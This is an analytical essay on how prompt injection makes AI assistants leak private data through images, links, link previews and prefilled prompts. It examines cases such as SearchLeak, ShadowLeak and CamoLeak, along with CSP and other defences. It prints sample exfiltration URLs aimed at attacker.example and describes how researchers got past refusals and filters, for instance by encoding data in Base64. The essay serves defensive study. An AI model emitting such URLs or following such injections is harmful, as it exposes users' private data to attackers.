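People click links in personalised phishing emails more often than in generic ones. *A Large-Scale Study of Personalized Phishing using Large Language Models* tested emails that a language model wrote to some of its 7,700 participants using what it found about them on the web. According to Phishing Tackle, a company that covered the study, the click rates were 10.0% for these emails and about 4% for generic ones. Emails that the researchers personalised by hand for 100 people had a click rate of 24.2%. *Evaluating Large Language Models’ Ability to Automate Spear Phishing* (Heiding, Lermen and colleagues, 2026), an experiment with 101 participants, reports click rates of 54% for AI-personalised emails and 12% for the control group.

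Some differences between these emails and an assistant's answer suggest that links in the answer would have a higher click rate. The user has asked for the answer and will almost certainly read it, whereas many recipients never open a test email. In the campaigns where Hydari and colleagues had data on this, staff opened only 35% of the emails. Combined with the overall click rate, this suggests that roughly a third of those who opened an email clicked, although the two figures don't cover the same set of campaigns. Employers also warn staff about links in emails far more than about links in a chat with an assistant. But a user who already has a satisfactory answer has little reason to click anything, and the model may garble the attacker's pretext or leave it out.

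A click is also more likely to cause harm in a one-click leak than in ordinary phishing, because the click itself sends the data. In the university's campaigns, 12.47% of emails led to a click, but where the test included a fake login page, only 2.99% led someone to submit a password. The password rate is closer to the real damage from ordinary phishing, but the click rate is the better estimate for a one-click leak. A click rate of around 10% seems a fair working assumption for a plausible link, though it could be much higher for a link that fits the user's question as well as the one in Slack AI did.

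### Images and links compared

| | Image that loads by itself | Link in the answer |
|---|---|---|
| Probability, once the answer is displayed | Close to certain if nothing blocks the image | Depends on whether the user clicks |
| Timing | Immediately | Whenever the user clicks, if ever |
| What the user can see | Often nothing | The label, and the address if the user checks |
| Data per request | As much as fits in an address | The same |
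| Repetition | Can happen every time the answer is displayed | Needs a new click each time |

The need for a click protects a secret less when more people have access to it. If only one person's assistant can read the secret, a 10% click rate means that nine attempts in ten fail. But if twenty employees can all read the same customer list, and each sees the attacker's link once and decides independently whether to click, the chance that at least one of them clicks is 1 − 0.9²⁰, or about 88%.

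The delay helps the defender more, because the company can find and delete the answer before anybody clicks, and a short-lived secret such as a login code may expire first.

A link and an image can each carry the same amount of data in a single request, but an answer can contain many images, and the browser will request them all. In *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, Willison describes a January 2026 attack on the email app Superhuman that used images to send out content from dozens of a user's emails after a request to summarise recent mail. An attacker using links would have to fit everything into one address or persuade the user to click repeatedly.

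Unlike an image, a link opens a whole web page, which can run scripts and ask the user for more information, such as a password. The browser's normal separation between websites still prevents the page from reading the chat, so the attacker gets only what the model put in the address and whatever the user then enters on the page.

Repeated leaks are also easier with images. If the injected instructions stay in the context, the model can add a new image to every answer, and the user may never notice. A new link in every answer would soon look odd. With links, an attacker is more likely to succeed by waiting and trying again with a different pretext, since more than half of the hospital staff clicked at least once over eight months.

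## Link previews, prefilled prompts and other cases between the two

A link in an assistant's answer normally sends no data until the user clicks it. But many people now talk to AI agents through messaging apps such as Slack, Teams and Telegram, which may open the link automatically to show a preview. In some other attacks, the user clicks once, on a link that arrives before the assistant has written anything, and the data is then sent automatically. It helps to classify these cases by which program contacts the attacker's server and what a careful user could have refused to do.

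### Link previews in messaging apps

When someone posts a link in a messaging app, the app often fetches the page and shows a link preview with the page's title and a picture, a process developers call unfurling. If hidden instructions lead an AI agent to post a link with private data in the address, fetching the preview sends that data to the attacker.

In August 2024, Rehberger warned that link previews could leak data from chatbot conversations, in Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*. Slack's documentation said that it unfurled all links by default, whether a person or an app had posted them. When Rehberger had a program post a link in Slack, the linked website logged a visit from "Slackbot-LinkExpanding", which is good evidence that Slack fetched links automatically. The article also explains how instructions on a web page could make a chatbot add part of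 the earlier conversation to such a link, but it doesn't name a particular chatbot that had leaked data in this way.

*The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* (Willison, 2024) is a short post about Rehberger's article. Willison called link unfurling a vulnerability he hadn't thought about before and noted that Discord fetches links too. The post appeared one day after PromptArmor published its attack on Slack AI, in which the developer had to click a link.

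When a messaging app previews a link, the messaging company's server requests the URL as soon as the agent's message arrives. The leak is therefore zero-click, and it happens before the user can inspect the link. Even afterwards the link may look harmless, because the attacker can have the agent write the data in invisible characters, a technique called ASCII smuggling.

Slack lets the developer of a bot turn previews off by adding two settings to each message the bot posts, one for links to pages and one for links to media:

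```
{
  "text": "Here is the summary you asked for.",
  "unfurl_links": false,
  "unfurl_media": false
}
```

The link still appears in the message and still works, so the leak goes back to needing a click.

In February 2026, PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* reported that the problem had become more common as people connected agents to the apps they already used. Its main example is OpenClaw, an AI agent that users can instruct through Telegram and other apps. With the default Telegram configuration, a link in an OpenClaw message produced a preview, and the preview request included the data in the link's URL.

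PromptArmor also set up a website where people can test their own combination of agent and app. The user has the agent post a link to the site with test data in the URL. If the app fetches a preview, the site shows the data it received and which company's preview program made the request. Users can then report the combination as risky, or as apparently safe if no request arrived. Apostol's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* lists Microsoft Teams with agents made in Copilot Studio, and Slack with certain bots, among the risky combinations.

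These reports come from volunteers, whose settings may differ, so they can't be used to estimate what share of agents is exposed. The test also covers only the last stage of an attack. A combination that fails it will leak data if an injection succeeds, but the test doesn't measure how susceptible that agent is to injection.

OpenClaw users can fix the problem by adding `linkPreview: false` to the Telegram section of the agent's configuration file. PromptArmor says that repeating its test after this change will no longer send the data to its site. It also wants messaging companies to let people turn off previews for individual chats or channels, so that a company could keep them for conversations between colleagues. For now, the person who sets up the agent has to know about the risk in advance, and may not be the person who reads its messages.

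### Whether browsers open links in advance

Browsers can fetch a linked page before the user clicks, so that it opens faster. This is called prefetching, and it would turn a one-click leak in a web chat into a zero-click one. A link doesn't normally trigger prefetching just by appearing on a page. The page's own code has to request it, either for a particular address or, in Chrome, through rules that can apply to any link the pointer rests on. The model can't write such a request in Markdown, so the risk arises mainly if the developers of a chat page turn on prefetching for links to outside websites, which they have little reason to do.

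A browser may also look up the server address for a link's host name before the user clicks. This lookup doesn't include the path or query string, so it doesn't reveal a login code placed in either. But a code in the host name, as in `482913.attacker.example`, could reach the attacker, who can run the server that answers lookups for that domain. Browsers have generally not made these automatic lookups for links on encrypted pages, and nearly every chat page is encrypted.

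None of the attacks on Slack AI, ChatGPT and Copilot described so far depended on prefetching. Link-safety scanners are probably a bigger concern because they may visit a link that no one has clicked. This seems to have happened with the documents that Copilot created in ReLeak.

### Opening a message from one's own agent

An attack on Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, an agent that carries out office tasks, is harder to classify. Willison (2026) explains in *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* that the agent could email the user without asking for approval. An injection could make it include an image from an outside server in such an email, with private data in the image's address. The data went to that server when the user opened the message.

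This leak is better described as zero-click, even though opening an email usually takes a click. People can learn not to open suspicious emails, but this one came from the user's own assistant, and reading what the assistant sends is part of using it. Even a careful person would have had no reason not to open it. Similarly, the approval rule may have seemed reasonable to its designers because an email to oneself doesn't look like communication with the outside world.

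The attack also got around the limit on how much data fits in an address. OneDrive can create download links that work without a login. These links are short enough to fit in an address, and an attacker who receives one can download the whole file.

### A click that starts the attack

Security researchers also use "one-click" for attacks in which the click comes at the beginning. Many assistants let a link fill in the user's prompt. A link such as this one opens the assistant with a question already in the text box:

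`https://assistant.example/?q=opening+hours+of+the+museum`

Prefilling a prompt through a link is convenient for bookmarks and for buttons on other websites. Some assistants also submit the prompt as soon as the page opens, so an attacker can write instructions into a link, and anyone who clicks it while signed in sends those instructions to their own assistant. The data security company Varonis, which published four such attacks in 2026, calls the technique parameter-to-prompt injection.

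A prefilled prompt differs from an indirect prompt injection in an email or web page because the attacker's text arrives where the user's own request would normally be. This means that a model trained to ignore instructions in emails may still follow the attacker's instructions, and that the attacker doesn't have to wait for the user to ask a suitable question.

### SearchLeak

SearchLeak is an attack on Enterprise Search, the Microsoft 365 Copilot feature that employees use to search their company's emails, meetings and files. Varonis published it on 15 June 2026. The attacker sends an employee a link by email, Teams, WhatsApp or any other channel. The link opens Microsoft's real search page, so filters that block known malicious websites let it through. The link contains instructions in place of a search term, and Copilot carries them out when the page opens.

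In Taler's demonstration, the instructions made Copilot find an email and put its title into the address of an image. Microsoft had two safeguards that should have stopped the browser from sending the request for that image to an attacker.

The first concerned HTML, the code of web pages. Copilot's answer contained the image as HTML, and Microsoft's page put such code inside a block that browsers display as plain text, to stop images from loading. But the page displayed the answer while Copilot was still writing it and added the block only at the end. In the meantime, the browser requested the image. Programmers call this a race condition because the result depends on which of two events happens first.

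The second safeguard was the page's Content Security Policy, which prevented the browser from loading images from the attacker's server. It did allow images from Bing, Microsoft's search engine. Bing has a feature for searching with a picture, which takes the picture's web address and fetches it. The attacker could therefore hide one address inside another, in roughly this form:

`https://permitted.example/search?image=https://attacker.example/Your_Security_Code_482913/img.png`

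The browser contacted Bing, which the policy allowed. Bing's server then requested the picture from the attacker's server, whose log recorded the title of the email, including the security code. EchoLeak had used a Microsoft Teams service for the same purpose a year earlier.

The attack needed all three weaknesses. If Copilot had not run the prefilled prompt, the attacker could not have got the image into the answer. If the page had neutralised the HTML before displaying any of it, the browser would have shown harmless text. If the request had not gone through Bing, the policy would have blocked it.

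When the employee clicked the link, it contained only the attacker's instructions, and Copilot had not yet searched for anything. The private data left afterwards, through an image that the browser loaded automatically. The employee might have briefly seen Copilot working and then an odd answer, but by then the browser had already sent the request. SearchLeak was thus a one-click attack whose second half worked like a zero-click leak, and removing every clickable link from Copilot's answers would not have prevented it.

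The first link was the only one the employee could have chosen not to click. Taler recommends inspecting links before clicking them, especially links to Microsoft 365 with long, encoded query strings. That is a lot to expect of users, because the usual advice is to check whether a link leads to the real website, and this one did. The click rates from simulated phishing emails apply more directly here than to links in an assistant's answer, because the attacker's link can arrive in an ordinary email. The median click rate of 10% could even underestimate how often people click a link that passes the usual check.

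Taler's example took only the title of an email, but that is sometimes all an attacker needs, such as when the title contains a login code. Copilot searches with the employee's permissions, so the method could presumably also have reached the text of emails, meeting notes and files. Microsoft has since fixed the flaw on its servers. According to The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox*, the company has no evidence that anyone used it maliciously.

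### Reprompt

Varonis had described a related attack on the consumer version of Copilot in *Reprompt* (January 2026). That attack also began with a link that filled in and ran a prompt. Copilot can open web pages to answer a question, and the prompt told it to open an address that contained the user's data. Because Copilot made the request itself, the attack didn't need an image or a link in the answer.

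Copilot had two protections against this. It usually refused to open an address without a good reason, and it could remove sensitive data from the address before opening it. The researchers supplied a reason by presenting the task as a puzzle, in which Copilot had to assemble an address from several parts, including the user's name, and identify the bird in the picture there. They then found that Copilot removed the data only from the first request. When the prompt told it to do everything twice and compare the results, Copilot removed a secret test phrase from the first address but left it in the second.

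Copilot also read the replies from the attacker's server, which could answer each request with a new instruction. This made the attack much more flexible than an image leak. In the demonstration, the instructions were to send the user's time, then their location, then everything Copilot had learned about them, and finally a summary of the last conversation. Someone who examined the original link would not have found most of these instructions in it.

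Taler said in Ars Technica's *A single click mounted a covert, multistage attack against Copilot* (2026) that the attack continued even if the user closed the tab immediately after clicking. An image leak, by contrast, works only if the page stays open until the browser has requested the image.

Varonis argues that Reprompt is fundamentally different from EchoLeak because the user doesn't have to type anything. But Reprompt required the user to click a stranger's link, and EchoLeak did not. EchoLeak was harder to avoid, but Reprompt gave the attacker more control over when the attack began.

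Microsoft received the report in August 2025 and fixed the flaw in January 2026. The fix covered the consumer product, and Varonis said at the time that companies using Microsoft 365 Copilot were not affected. SearchLeak later used the same first step against Microsoft 365 Copilot.

### CoSnitch

Varonis' *CoSnitch*, published on 18 August 2026, describes another attack on the consumer Copilot. The usual parameter, `q`, only filled in the text box, so a careful user who had clicked the link could still read the attacker's instructions and choose not to press Enter. But adding an undocumented second parameter to the link made Copilot run the prompt as soon as the page loaded.

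The researchers learned about the parameter from Copilot. When they asked how a prompt could run automatically, it replied that this was impossible. They kept asking why, and Copilot named the parameter in one of its explanations and described how Microsoft had supposedly disabled it. They built a link with the parameter, and it worked.

As in Reprompt, the data left when Copilot opened an address. The prompt could also draw on services the user had connected to Copilot, such as Gmail, Google Drive and a calendar. In one test, Copilot retrieved an email containing a password in plain text. The attacker's prompt can make Copilot convert such data to Base64, a standard way to encode data as letters, digits and a few symbols. Anyone can decode it, but a filter that checks outgoing requests for passwords may not recognise encoded ones.

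Varonis found a separate flaw that could make a click unnecessary in later conversations. When a user asked Copilot to summarise a web page, hidden instructions on the page could write entries into Copilot's long-term memory, where they stayed until the user deleted them. Microsoft lists links with prefilled prompts as another way to plant such entries, so a user might click a link in one conversation and be affected weeks later in another. Varonis showed that planted memories could change Copilot's answers, for instance by making it call a known software flaw harmless, but did not demonstrate a data leak that began this way.

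Varonis reported CoSnitch in December 2025, and Microsoft released the patches about eight months later. Varonis said it had seen no evidence of real attacks.

### RovoBlast

The same technique also worked on Rovo, Atlassian's AI assistant. Companies use Atlassian's software to track tasks (Jira) and share internal documents (Confluence). Rovo can also search other services a company connects to it, including Slack, Microsoft 365 and Google Workspace. Atlassian offers connectors for more than 50 platforms.

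Varonis' *RovoBlast* (7 August 2026) describes a link that fills in Rovo's prompt, which the assistant then runs without warning the user or asking for confirmation. Links to Rovo normally include an identifier for the user's company, but if the attacker left it blank, Atlassian's website would send each user to their own company's Rovo. A single link could therefore work on employees of many companies.

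The researchers got the data out through ResearchAgent, a tool Rovo uses to search the web and move through websites in several steps. The attacker's prompt could make Rovo collect internal information and send it to an outside website as part of its "research". Rovo rarely refused, so the researchers didn't need to have it repeat requests as they had in Reprompt. Varonis describes the exfiltration step in less detail than in its reports on Copilot, and it learned what the tools could do partly by asking Rovo, which is not always reliable. *Researchers Uncover RovoBlast Vulnerability in Atlassian AI Assistant* (Mascellino, 2026) confirms that Atlassian accepted the report and fixed the flaw.

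SearchLeak fits Willison's definition of the lethal trifecta well enough. The third condition is an ability to communicate externally, and Copilot had that ability as long as the user's browser loaded images from addresses that Copilot had written. Varonis compares its findings with the trifecta but points out that Copilot had no internet access of its own, and for this reason describes such attacks as "Enter, Evade, Escape" instead.

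### ShadowLeak: a request from the assistant's own servers

In Reprompt and CoSnitch, a click started the attack and Copilot made the request. In ShadowLeak, which the security company Radware disclosed in September 2025, an assistant could make such a request without a click.

Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes an attack on Deep Research, a ChatGPT feature that spends five to 30 minutes reading websites and other sources before it writes a report. Users can connect it to their Gmail accounts. The attacker sends the user an email about a company restructuring that includes instructions, which the attacker can hide in tiny or white text. The user later asks Deep Research to search the day's emails for information about a new employee. Deep Research reads the attacker's email and a genuine one from HR, then opens a URL on the attacker's server with the employee's name and home address in it.

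The researchers needed several attempts to get Deep Research to send the data to the attacker's address. It blocked a plain instruction to send the data and another that claimed the user had requested it. It treated the address as suspicious and searched the web for it instead of opening it. The researchers then found the name of the internal tool that opens web pages and mentioned it in the email, which worked some of the time. Telling the agent to try again after a failure improved the results, but it still left out the personal data in some attempts.

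The version that worked told the agent to encode the data in Base64 first, supposedly for security. Radware believes this succeeded because the software that made the request received only a meaningless-looking string and did not recognise it as personal data. Radware reports a 100% success rate in repeated tests but does not say how many it ran.

The method used in ShadowLeak has a drawback for attackers. The agent had to use a tool to open an address, and OpenAI had put more safeguards around that step. To leak data through an image, the model only has to write an address.

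When the agent opened the address, the request went from OpenAI's servers to the attacker's, so a Content Security Policy in the user's browser had no effect on it. Neither an employer's web filter nor security software on the user's computer could detect it. ChatGPT already restricted which addresses it would display images from, but Radware found no comparable restriction on the pages that Deep Research could open.

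ShadowLeak was a zero-click leak, because it required only normal use of the product and nothing suspicious appeared on the screen for a careful user to refuse. A press release from Radware (2025) slightly overstates this by describing the attack as needing no clicks or prompts, since the user had to connect Gmail and start a research task.

Radware reported the flaw on 18 June 2025. OpenAI fixed it in early August and confirmed the fix on 3 September. The check on automatically fetched addresses that OpenAI described in January 2026 is meant to prevent such leaks. Anthropic uses a stricter rule for the tool Claude uses to open web pages. Willison (2026) explains in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* that Claude may open only the exact addresses that the user has typed or its own search tool has returned. This prevents an injection from simply attaching a secret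 to an address, but Ayush Paul's attack in July 2026 exploited a gap in that design too.

### Sorting the cases by their clicks

"One-click" and "zero-click" are less ambiguous when applied separately to starting the attack and to sending the data. An attack could need a click for each, for example if a prefilled prompt produced a link that the user then had to follow. An attacker would have little reason to choose this unless the assistant had no automatic way to send data out.

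| Case | Click needed to start the attack? | Click needed to send the data? | What contacts the attacker's server |
|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak, final version | No | No | Microsoft Teams' server |
| Link preview of an agent's message | No | No | The messaging app's server |
| ShadowLeak | No | No | OpenAI's server |
| Copilot Cowork | No | Only to open the agent's email | The program that displays the email |
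| Slack AI | No | Yes | The user's browser |
| SearchLeak | Yes | No | Bing's server |
| Reprompt and CoSnitch | Yes | No | Copilot's page-opening tool |
| RovoBlast | Yes | No | Rovo's ResearchAgent |

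## Why restricting image addresses leaves links open

Developers have three main ways to stop an image in an answer from sending data to an attacker. A sanitizer removes the image before the page displays the answer. A Content Security Policy (CSP) makes the browser refuse to request it. An image proxy puts the company's own server between the browser and the outside server. Together they can prevent almost all leaks through images, but a link with the same data in its address can still send that data to the attacker.

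### Where each control acts

The sanitizer acts first, on the model's text. Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025) lists Gemini's sanitizer among five defences. The sanitizer removes every external image, so Google doesn't need to keep a list of safe servers, but Gemini can't show users pictures by linking to other websites.

A sanitizer works only if it recognises every way of writing an image and finishes before the page displays anything. Copilot's filter missed one notation in EchoLeak, and in SearchLeak the page neutralised the image too late.

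A CSP acts later, in the browser. The company sends it along with the chat page, for example:

`Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'self'; img-src 'self' https://images.assistant.example`

Here `'self'` stands for the chat page's own site. The `img-src` rule lists the servers from which the browser may load images, and `default-src` covers types of content that have no rule of their own. *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft of the World Wide Web Consortium (W3C) standard, says that the browser compares an image's address with the list before requesting the image. If the address matches nothing on the list, the browser sends no request.

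This check applies however the model wrote the image, so it can catch an image that the sanitizer missed. Checkmarx recommends using both. W3C describes CSP as an extra layer of defence and warns that a strict image rule isn't enough by itself. If the policy has no `default-src`, a page can still send data through other kinds of request, such as prefetching. A rule that permits every server also undoes the protection, even if the other rules are strict.

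GitHub, a website for storing and sharing code, uses an image proxy called Camo. When a developer saves a project description that includes a picture from another website, GitHub replaces the picture's address with one on Camo and adds a cryptographic signature. When someone reads the description, their browser requests the picture from Camo, which checks the signature, fetches the picture from the original server and sends it to the browser.

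The reader's browser never connects to the outside server, which protects the reader's network address. But if the proxy fetched any address the model wrote, it would send the stolen data along with the request. To prevent this, the proxy requires a signature on each address. Neither the attacker nor the model can produce one, so the model can use only addresses that GitHub signed before the private data was in the context.

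### When a permitted server passes the data on

A CSP controls which servers the browser contacts, but not what those servers do next. Reddy and Gujral describe how a permitted Microsoft Teams service contacted the attacker's server in EchoLeak. Bing did the same in SearchLeak and ReLeak.

In these attacks, the Teams and Bing services fetched the attacker's address themselves, so the browser checked only its own request to those permitted services. A simple redirect from a permitted server would not have worked, because the browser also checks the new address against the policy.

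A permitted server can also leak data without forwarding it, if it stores the data where the attacker can read it. The January 2026 attack on the email app Superhuman worked this way. PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* explains that the app's CSP blocked images from unknown servers but allowed them from docs.google.com, which also hosts Google Forms. The attacker created a form, and the injected instructions made the assistant output an image link whose address filled in the form with the contents of the user's emails. When Google's server received the request, it saved the emails as a response to the form. Willison (2026) identified the CSP rule as the root cause and credited Superhuman with treating the report as a high priority and fixing the flaw.

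OpenAI's Codex had a similar flaw a few months later. PromptArmor showed that when a user asked Codex to sort through incoming email, an image could again send the user's legal correspondence and financial plans to an attacker's Google Form. PromptArmor reported the flaw on 21 April 2026, and OpenAI has since fixed it.

Allowlists can also go out of date. In September 2025, Willison described an attack on Salesforce's AI agent, which handles information about potential customers. Salesforce's CSP still permitted images from a domain whose registration had expired. Researchers registered the domain and received customer data in their own server logs.

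Developers can reduce these problems by keeping the list short and checking what each permitted server can do. For example, PromptArmor advised Notion to make sure attackers couldn't use its image server to get around the CSP. Permitting only one folder on a large site helps less than it might seem, because browsers ignore the folder part of a rule after a redirect. The W3C specified this behavior so that a malicious page couldn't use the rule to learn where other websites redirect their visitors.

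### CamoLeak

GitHub had a strict CSP and its signing proxy, but its assistant, Copilot Chat, still leaked private code through images. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes the flaw, which a researcher at the company found in June 2025. The flaw has a severity score of 9.6 out of 10.

The attacker proposes a change to a project and hides instructions in the description, inside a comment that GitHub doesn't display. When another developer asks Copilot Chat to explain the proposal, the instructions enter its context. Copilot Chat can read whatever that developer can read, including private projects.

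The first working version of the attack used a link. Copilot Chat encoded the contents of a private project and added them to the link's address. Clicking the link sent the data out despite GitHub's CSP and image proxy.

Removing the click was harder because the CSP blocked images from outside servers and Camo refused addresses without a valid signature. But the signature only prevented changes to an address, so the model could still use any signed addresses in any order. The researcher therefore had GitHub sign addresses in advance, one for each letter and symbol, all leading to the researcher's server. The injected instructions made Copilot Chat spell out the secret as a row of invisible images, and the order of the requests to the server revealed the text.

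The choice among these addresses conveyed the information, although none of them contained private data. With ten addresses, one for each digit, an attacker needs six images to send the code 482913. More generally, each choice among N addresses conveys log₂ N bits, so a set of 64 conveys six bits per image.

In a demonstration, the researcher stole the description of an undisclosed security flaw from a private project. The researcher also used the method to find and send out an access key for Amazon's cloud service.

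GitHub fixed the problem on 14 August 2025 by turning off images in Copilot Chat. The news became public on 8 October, according to OECD's *GitHub Copilot Chat Vulnerability Exposes Private Code and Secrets* (2025). This fix is about as complete as an image control can be, but it would not have stopped the researcher's first version of the attack, which needed only a link. Legit Security mentions no separate change to links.

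### The same code in an image and in a link

Suppose a company has closed all these gaps. Its sanitizer recognises every way of writing an image, and its CSP permits images only from the company's own site, which forwards nothing. The assistant has just read the two emails from the login-code example. If the injection succeeds, the model can put the same address in an image or a link:

```
![Banner](https://attacker.example/v?c=482913)

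[View the full newsletter](https://attacker.example/v?c=482913)
```

| Stage | Image | Link |
|---|---|---|
| The sanitizer processes the answer | It removes the image, because the address is on an outside server | It leaves the link in place |
| The page displays the answer | No image appears | The words "View the full newsletter" appear |
| The browser applies the CSP | It would block the request if the sanitizer had missed the image | It has no request to check yet |
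| The user clicks | There is nothing to click | The browser opens the address, because `img-src` doesn't apply |
| The attacker's server log | Empty | Contains `c=482913` |

Changing the image rule to `img-src 'none'`, which forbids all images, would not affect the link. Using `default-src 'none'` would not affect it either, because that rule covers only content the page loads.

In 2024, the assistant in Google Colab, a service for writing and running code in the browser, began to read the contents of users' notebooks. Google had already blocked data exfiltration through images, but Embrace The Red still demonstrated a prompt injection that used links.

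### The argument in four premises

The example is an instance of a more general argument:

1. The image controls govern content that the page loads.
2. Following a link is navigation, which these controls do not govern.
3. A link's address can hold the same data as an image's.
4. An assistant that cites the open web must show links to sites that its developers can't list in advance.

Premises 1 to 3 alone imply that data can still leak through links even if the image control is perfect. Premise 4 is why the company can't simply apply its short list of image servers to links too.

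`img-src` doesn't restrict links because W3C limits the rule to requests that load images. An image proxy likewise handles only the pictures that a page displays. A sanitizer can delete links as well as images, as Copilot's filter tried to do before EchoLeak, but it is then more than an image control, and the company has to decide which links to keep.

### The navigation rule that browsers never adopted

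Browsers could in principle apply an allowlist to links, and the people who write the CSP standard considered this for years. W3C's *No-external-navigation as potential csp3 feature* (2014) records an early suggestion to do so. In March 2018, Paicu proposed in *Intent to implement and ship* (2018) that Chrome add a rule called `navigate-to`, which would have let a page restrict where its links, forms and scripts could take the user. Six days later, Paicu (2018) announced that the draft standard included the rule.

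That October, José Moyano Gutiérrez complained on W3C's mailing list that CSP did not stop an attacker from stealing information by sending the browser to another address. Someone replied that `navigate-to` would solve this. Janc (2018), of Google, agreed that it would restrict navigation but pointed out that an attacker who could run scripts on the page would have other ways to get data out. That objection matters less for AI assistants, because in the link attacks described so far, the attacker controlled some of the answer's text but could not run scripts on the chat page.

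Eriksson and Sabelfeld (2020), in *AutoNav*, tested experimental versions of the rule in Chrome and Firefox and found that a malicious website could also use it to spy on its visitors. Many websites have a private page that redirects people to a login page if they aren't signed in. The malicious site could send a visitor to the private page under a rule that permitted only one of the two addresses. It could then tell whether the visitor was signed in by whether the browser blocked the visit. This worked even against websites that had never used `navigate-to`.

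They also found that data could leak under an optional setting of the rule, which allowed redirects as long as the final destination was on the list. To find out where an address led, the browser had to request it, so it had already sent the data by the time it blocked the visit. Without that setting, the browser checked the address first and sent nothing if it wasn't on the list. A strict version of the rule could therefore have stopped a one-click leak to an unlisted server.

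Mozilla's *Remove (disabled by default) CSP directive `navigate-to`* notes that no browser ever released the rule and that it was removed from the standard in September 2022, amid concerns about leaks through redirects. The following month, a developer working on WebKit, the engine behind Apple's Safari, wrote that browser makers had shown little support for it beyond Chrome's experimental version.

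The August 2026 draft of the standard has two rules for navigation. One restricts where a page can send forms, and the other restricts which websites can embed the page. Neither applies to a click on an ordinary link. Another rule covers the "ping", an extra notification that a link can send when someone clicks it, but not the address that the link opens.

Frames, which display one web page inside another, are a partial exception. The `frame-src` rule restricts which addresses a frame can load. If a developer showed the assistant's answers in a frame and prevented links from opening outside it, the browser could check clicks against the rule. But this would be an awkward way to read a cited source, and the developer would still need a list of permitted sites.

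The second premise is therefore correct for current browsers, but only because of a standards decision that browser makers could reverse. If they revived `navigate-to`, a company would still have to decide which sites to allow.

### What a link can hold

Microsoft (2025) notes that an attacker can encode the user's data in the address of either an image or a link.

Image controls can make links better than images for sending a lot of data. In CamoLeak, GitHub's proxy limited the researcher to one character per image, but a single link could carry a long stretch of encoded code.

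### Assistants that could use a short list

The fourth premise depends on what the assistant is for. A general assistant with web search may cite a local newspaper in one answer and a manufacturer's manual in the next. Its developers can't know in advance every site it will cite, and refusing to link to unfamiliar sites would make its sources harder to check.

Even for ordinary websites, whose owners choose the links, it is difficult to list every permitted destination. Moyano Gutiérrez argued that most of them link to few outside pages and that these rarely change. Eriksson and Sabelfeld tested something close to this on 100 pages from each of 10,000 popular websites. For each site, their program built a list of permitted destinations from 80 pages and checked it against the other 20. The list covered every link on those 20 pages for only 42% of the sites. An assistant's links would presumably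 be harder to predict, because they depend on what the user asks.

Google's response to Checkmarx's report about links in Gemini also fits the premise. Google closed the report as "Won't Fix (Infeasible)" but gave no technical reason, and its written reply was mostly about the problem's severity.

The premise doesn't hold for an assistant that doesn't need to cite the open web. One that answers questions about a company's holiday policy might link only to the company's own documents, and a customer service agent might need only the help pages of a single product. Salesforce, for example, responded to the expired domain by correcting its CSP and introducing a "Trusted URLs" feature, which prevents its agent from generating links to sites that aren't on a list.

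For these assistants, a short list of permitted links can block most of the exfiltration that image restrictions miss. The list has to be chosen as carefully as a list of image servers. If it included docs.google.com, an attacker could exfiltrate data through a link to a Google Form, much as the attack on Superhuman did through an image, although the user would have to click the link.

A web assistant could also apply a rule like Claude's for opening pages and show only links whose exact addresses its search tool has returned or the user has typed. The fourth premise allows this, but the company would have to build the check specifically for links.

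### How much risk the image controls remove

Once images no longer load, they can't cause silent, automatic leaks, so it makes sense to fix images first. The remaining links leak data only when someone clicks them, and at the 10% click rate assumed earlier, a single link shown to one person would usually go unclicked. A company could therefore argue, with some justification, that blocking images removes most of the danger.

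But the attacker can try again by sending another email, which takes almost no effort. If each link independently has a 10% chance of being clicked, the chance that a user who sees seven links clicks at least one is 1 − 0.9⁷, or about 52%.

The image controls also don't reduce how much data a successful leak can expose, and they don't stop the injection, which can still give the user a reason to click a link.

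Restricting image addresses also doesn't stop every zero-click leak. ShadowLeak, attacks using link previews in messaging apps, and two of the three ReLeak attacks worked without an image in the answer.

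## Controls that act on links, and what still leaks

A company that has stopped data from leaking through images can also remove links, compare them with a list of sites, restrict the addresses its assistant may use, or warn the user before a link opens. Each option either deprives users of some useful links or lets some data through, and most do both.

### Removing links altogether

An injection could make Amazon Q for Business, Amazon's assistant for companies, write a link with the earlier conversation in its query string, which would leak if the user clicked. Amazon fixed this in January 2024 by stopping the assistant from outputting any links. Willison noted that Microsoft 365 Chat, part of what is now Microsoft 365 Copilot, apparently used the same fix. A year later Copilot was still removing links to outside websites, but Aim Labs got past the filter with markdown's reference notation.

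Removing links means nobody has to judge whether an address is safe. However, the filter has to recognise every link, including bare addresses, which many chat pages turn into links automatically. This is easier if the developer filters the answer after the page's code has converted the markdown, because by then every notation has become the same kind of HTML link.

Some data can still get out. The model can write the address as ordinary text and ask the user to copy it into the browser, though fewer people will do that than click a link. If the user pastes the answer into a messaging app, the app may fetch the address to show a preview. The filter also has to cover everything else the assistant produces. In ReLeak, the link was in a document that Copilot had saved.

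The drawback is that users can't easily check an answer that relies on the open web. This hardly matters for an assistant that answers only from a company's own files. In a less restrictive version for assistants that search the web, the model would write only a source number, and the chat page would supply the matching address from the search results. The model could then choose among those addresses but couldn't add anything to them.

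### Lists of bad sites and good ones

Gemini removes links to sites on Google's Safe Browsing list and keeps the rest. Users lose few legitimate links, since ordinary websites are rarely on the list, and the filter helps against phishing sites that Google already knows about.

Blocklists are poorly suited to stopping exfiltration. A site is listed after a person or an automated scanner notices it doing harm, and a newly registered domain has no history to check. A scanner can recognise a phishing site by its fake login page, but a server that collects data from the URLs it receives can answer every visitor with "page not found" or redirect them to a real newsletter. An attacker worried about being listed can also use a different domain for each victim.

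An allowlist excludes new domains, but an attacker can still use a well-known site. An earlier version of ChatGPT's address check, which OpenAI introduced in December 2023, had this problem. Before displaying an image, the chat page used it to check with OpenAI's servers that the image was safe. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025) explains that the check also covered links and always accepted addresses on bing.com. Bing's search results link to bing.com addresses that redirect to the chosen website. Tenable's researchers got their own site into Bing's results and used its bing.com address, and ChatGPT loaded their image.

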